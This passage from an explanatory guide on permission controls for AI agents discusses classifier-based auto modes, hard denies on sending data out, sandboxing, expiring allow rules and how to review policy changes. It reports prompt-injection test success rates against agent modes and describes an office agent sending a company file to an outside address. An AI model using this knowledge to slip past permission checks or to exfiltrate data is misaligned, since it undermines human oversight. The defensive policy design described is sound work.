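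Auto mode also has "hard denies" for actions such as sending code or secrets to an outside service. The classifier is meant never to approve these actions, so a user who wants to take one has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. But the classifier still has to detect that a command sends data out, which makes a hard deny less certain than a fixed rule on a tool's arguments.

Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, makes a similar division. According to Zhu and colleagues, it runs low-risk operations automatically and asks the user about high-risk ones, such as network access. It also has Auto-review and Full Access modes. Trajectory Labs, a company commissioned by Anthropic, tested both modes against prompt injection in July 2026. With GPT-5.6 Sol, 19.03% of attacks succeeded in Full Access mode and 5.83% in Auto-review mode.

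None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude models in auto mode. However, only 0.09% succeeded when Claude Code skipped all permission checks, so the models themselves resisted nearly all of the attacks. The attacks had been developed against an older Claude model, and OpenAI has since updated Auto-review.

A sandbox adds protection that does not depend on judging each command, because it isolates the agent from the rest of the computer and often from the network. But someone has to configure each new capability, and a task that needs the network requires an opening in the sandbox. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* still recommends using auto mode in an isolated environment.

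### Keeping the rules up to date

Each exception that a person approves can become a rule that nobody remembers the reason for. Shah and Kathrotia propose storing every approval with an identifier, the person responsible, the time and the number of uses. A permanent rule also needs a reason and an expiry date. If the company decides to let the office agent email Maria regularly, the record might look like this:

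| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Rule | Allow email to `maria@client.example` |
| Reason | She receives the monthly car summary |
| Owner | Ana |
| Approved | 3 December 2026 |
| Expires | 3 June 2027 |
| Times used | 0 |

In a layered policy, letting an allow rule expire does little harm. If the rule allowing emails to Maria expires, the next one goes to a human reviewer, who can approve it and renew the rule. The permission then lasts only if someone decides to keep it, whereas in security operations old rules stay until someone decides to remove them. A deny rule should not lapse this way, because that could, without anyone noticing, permit the action it was written to stop. Its expiry date should prompt a review instead. Exceptions to a deny rule can expire as allow rules do.

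Changes that widen a policy need stricter review than changes that tighten it, because mistaken permissions are harder to notice than mistaken denials. Reviewers should compare the calls each version permits, as Progent does, because the wording can mislead. For example, adding an exception to a deny rule makes the rule longer but permits more calls. Tightening can still interrupt legitimate work, so it is worth replaying recent normal runs first.

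After a failure, the company should first ask whether the agent needed the permission. Suppose the allowlist had permitted email to any address when the office agent sent `Cars/b.txt` to `drop@outside.example`. A deny rule for that address would still let the agent email every other outside address. If the company instead removed the general permission to email outsiders, a person would have to approve all such messages, including those to addresses nobody thought to list. A deny rule makes more sense when the agent needs the permission. The office agent cannot do its research without web searches, so the company might block only searches that contain text copied from company files.
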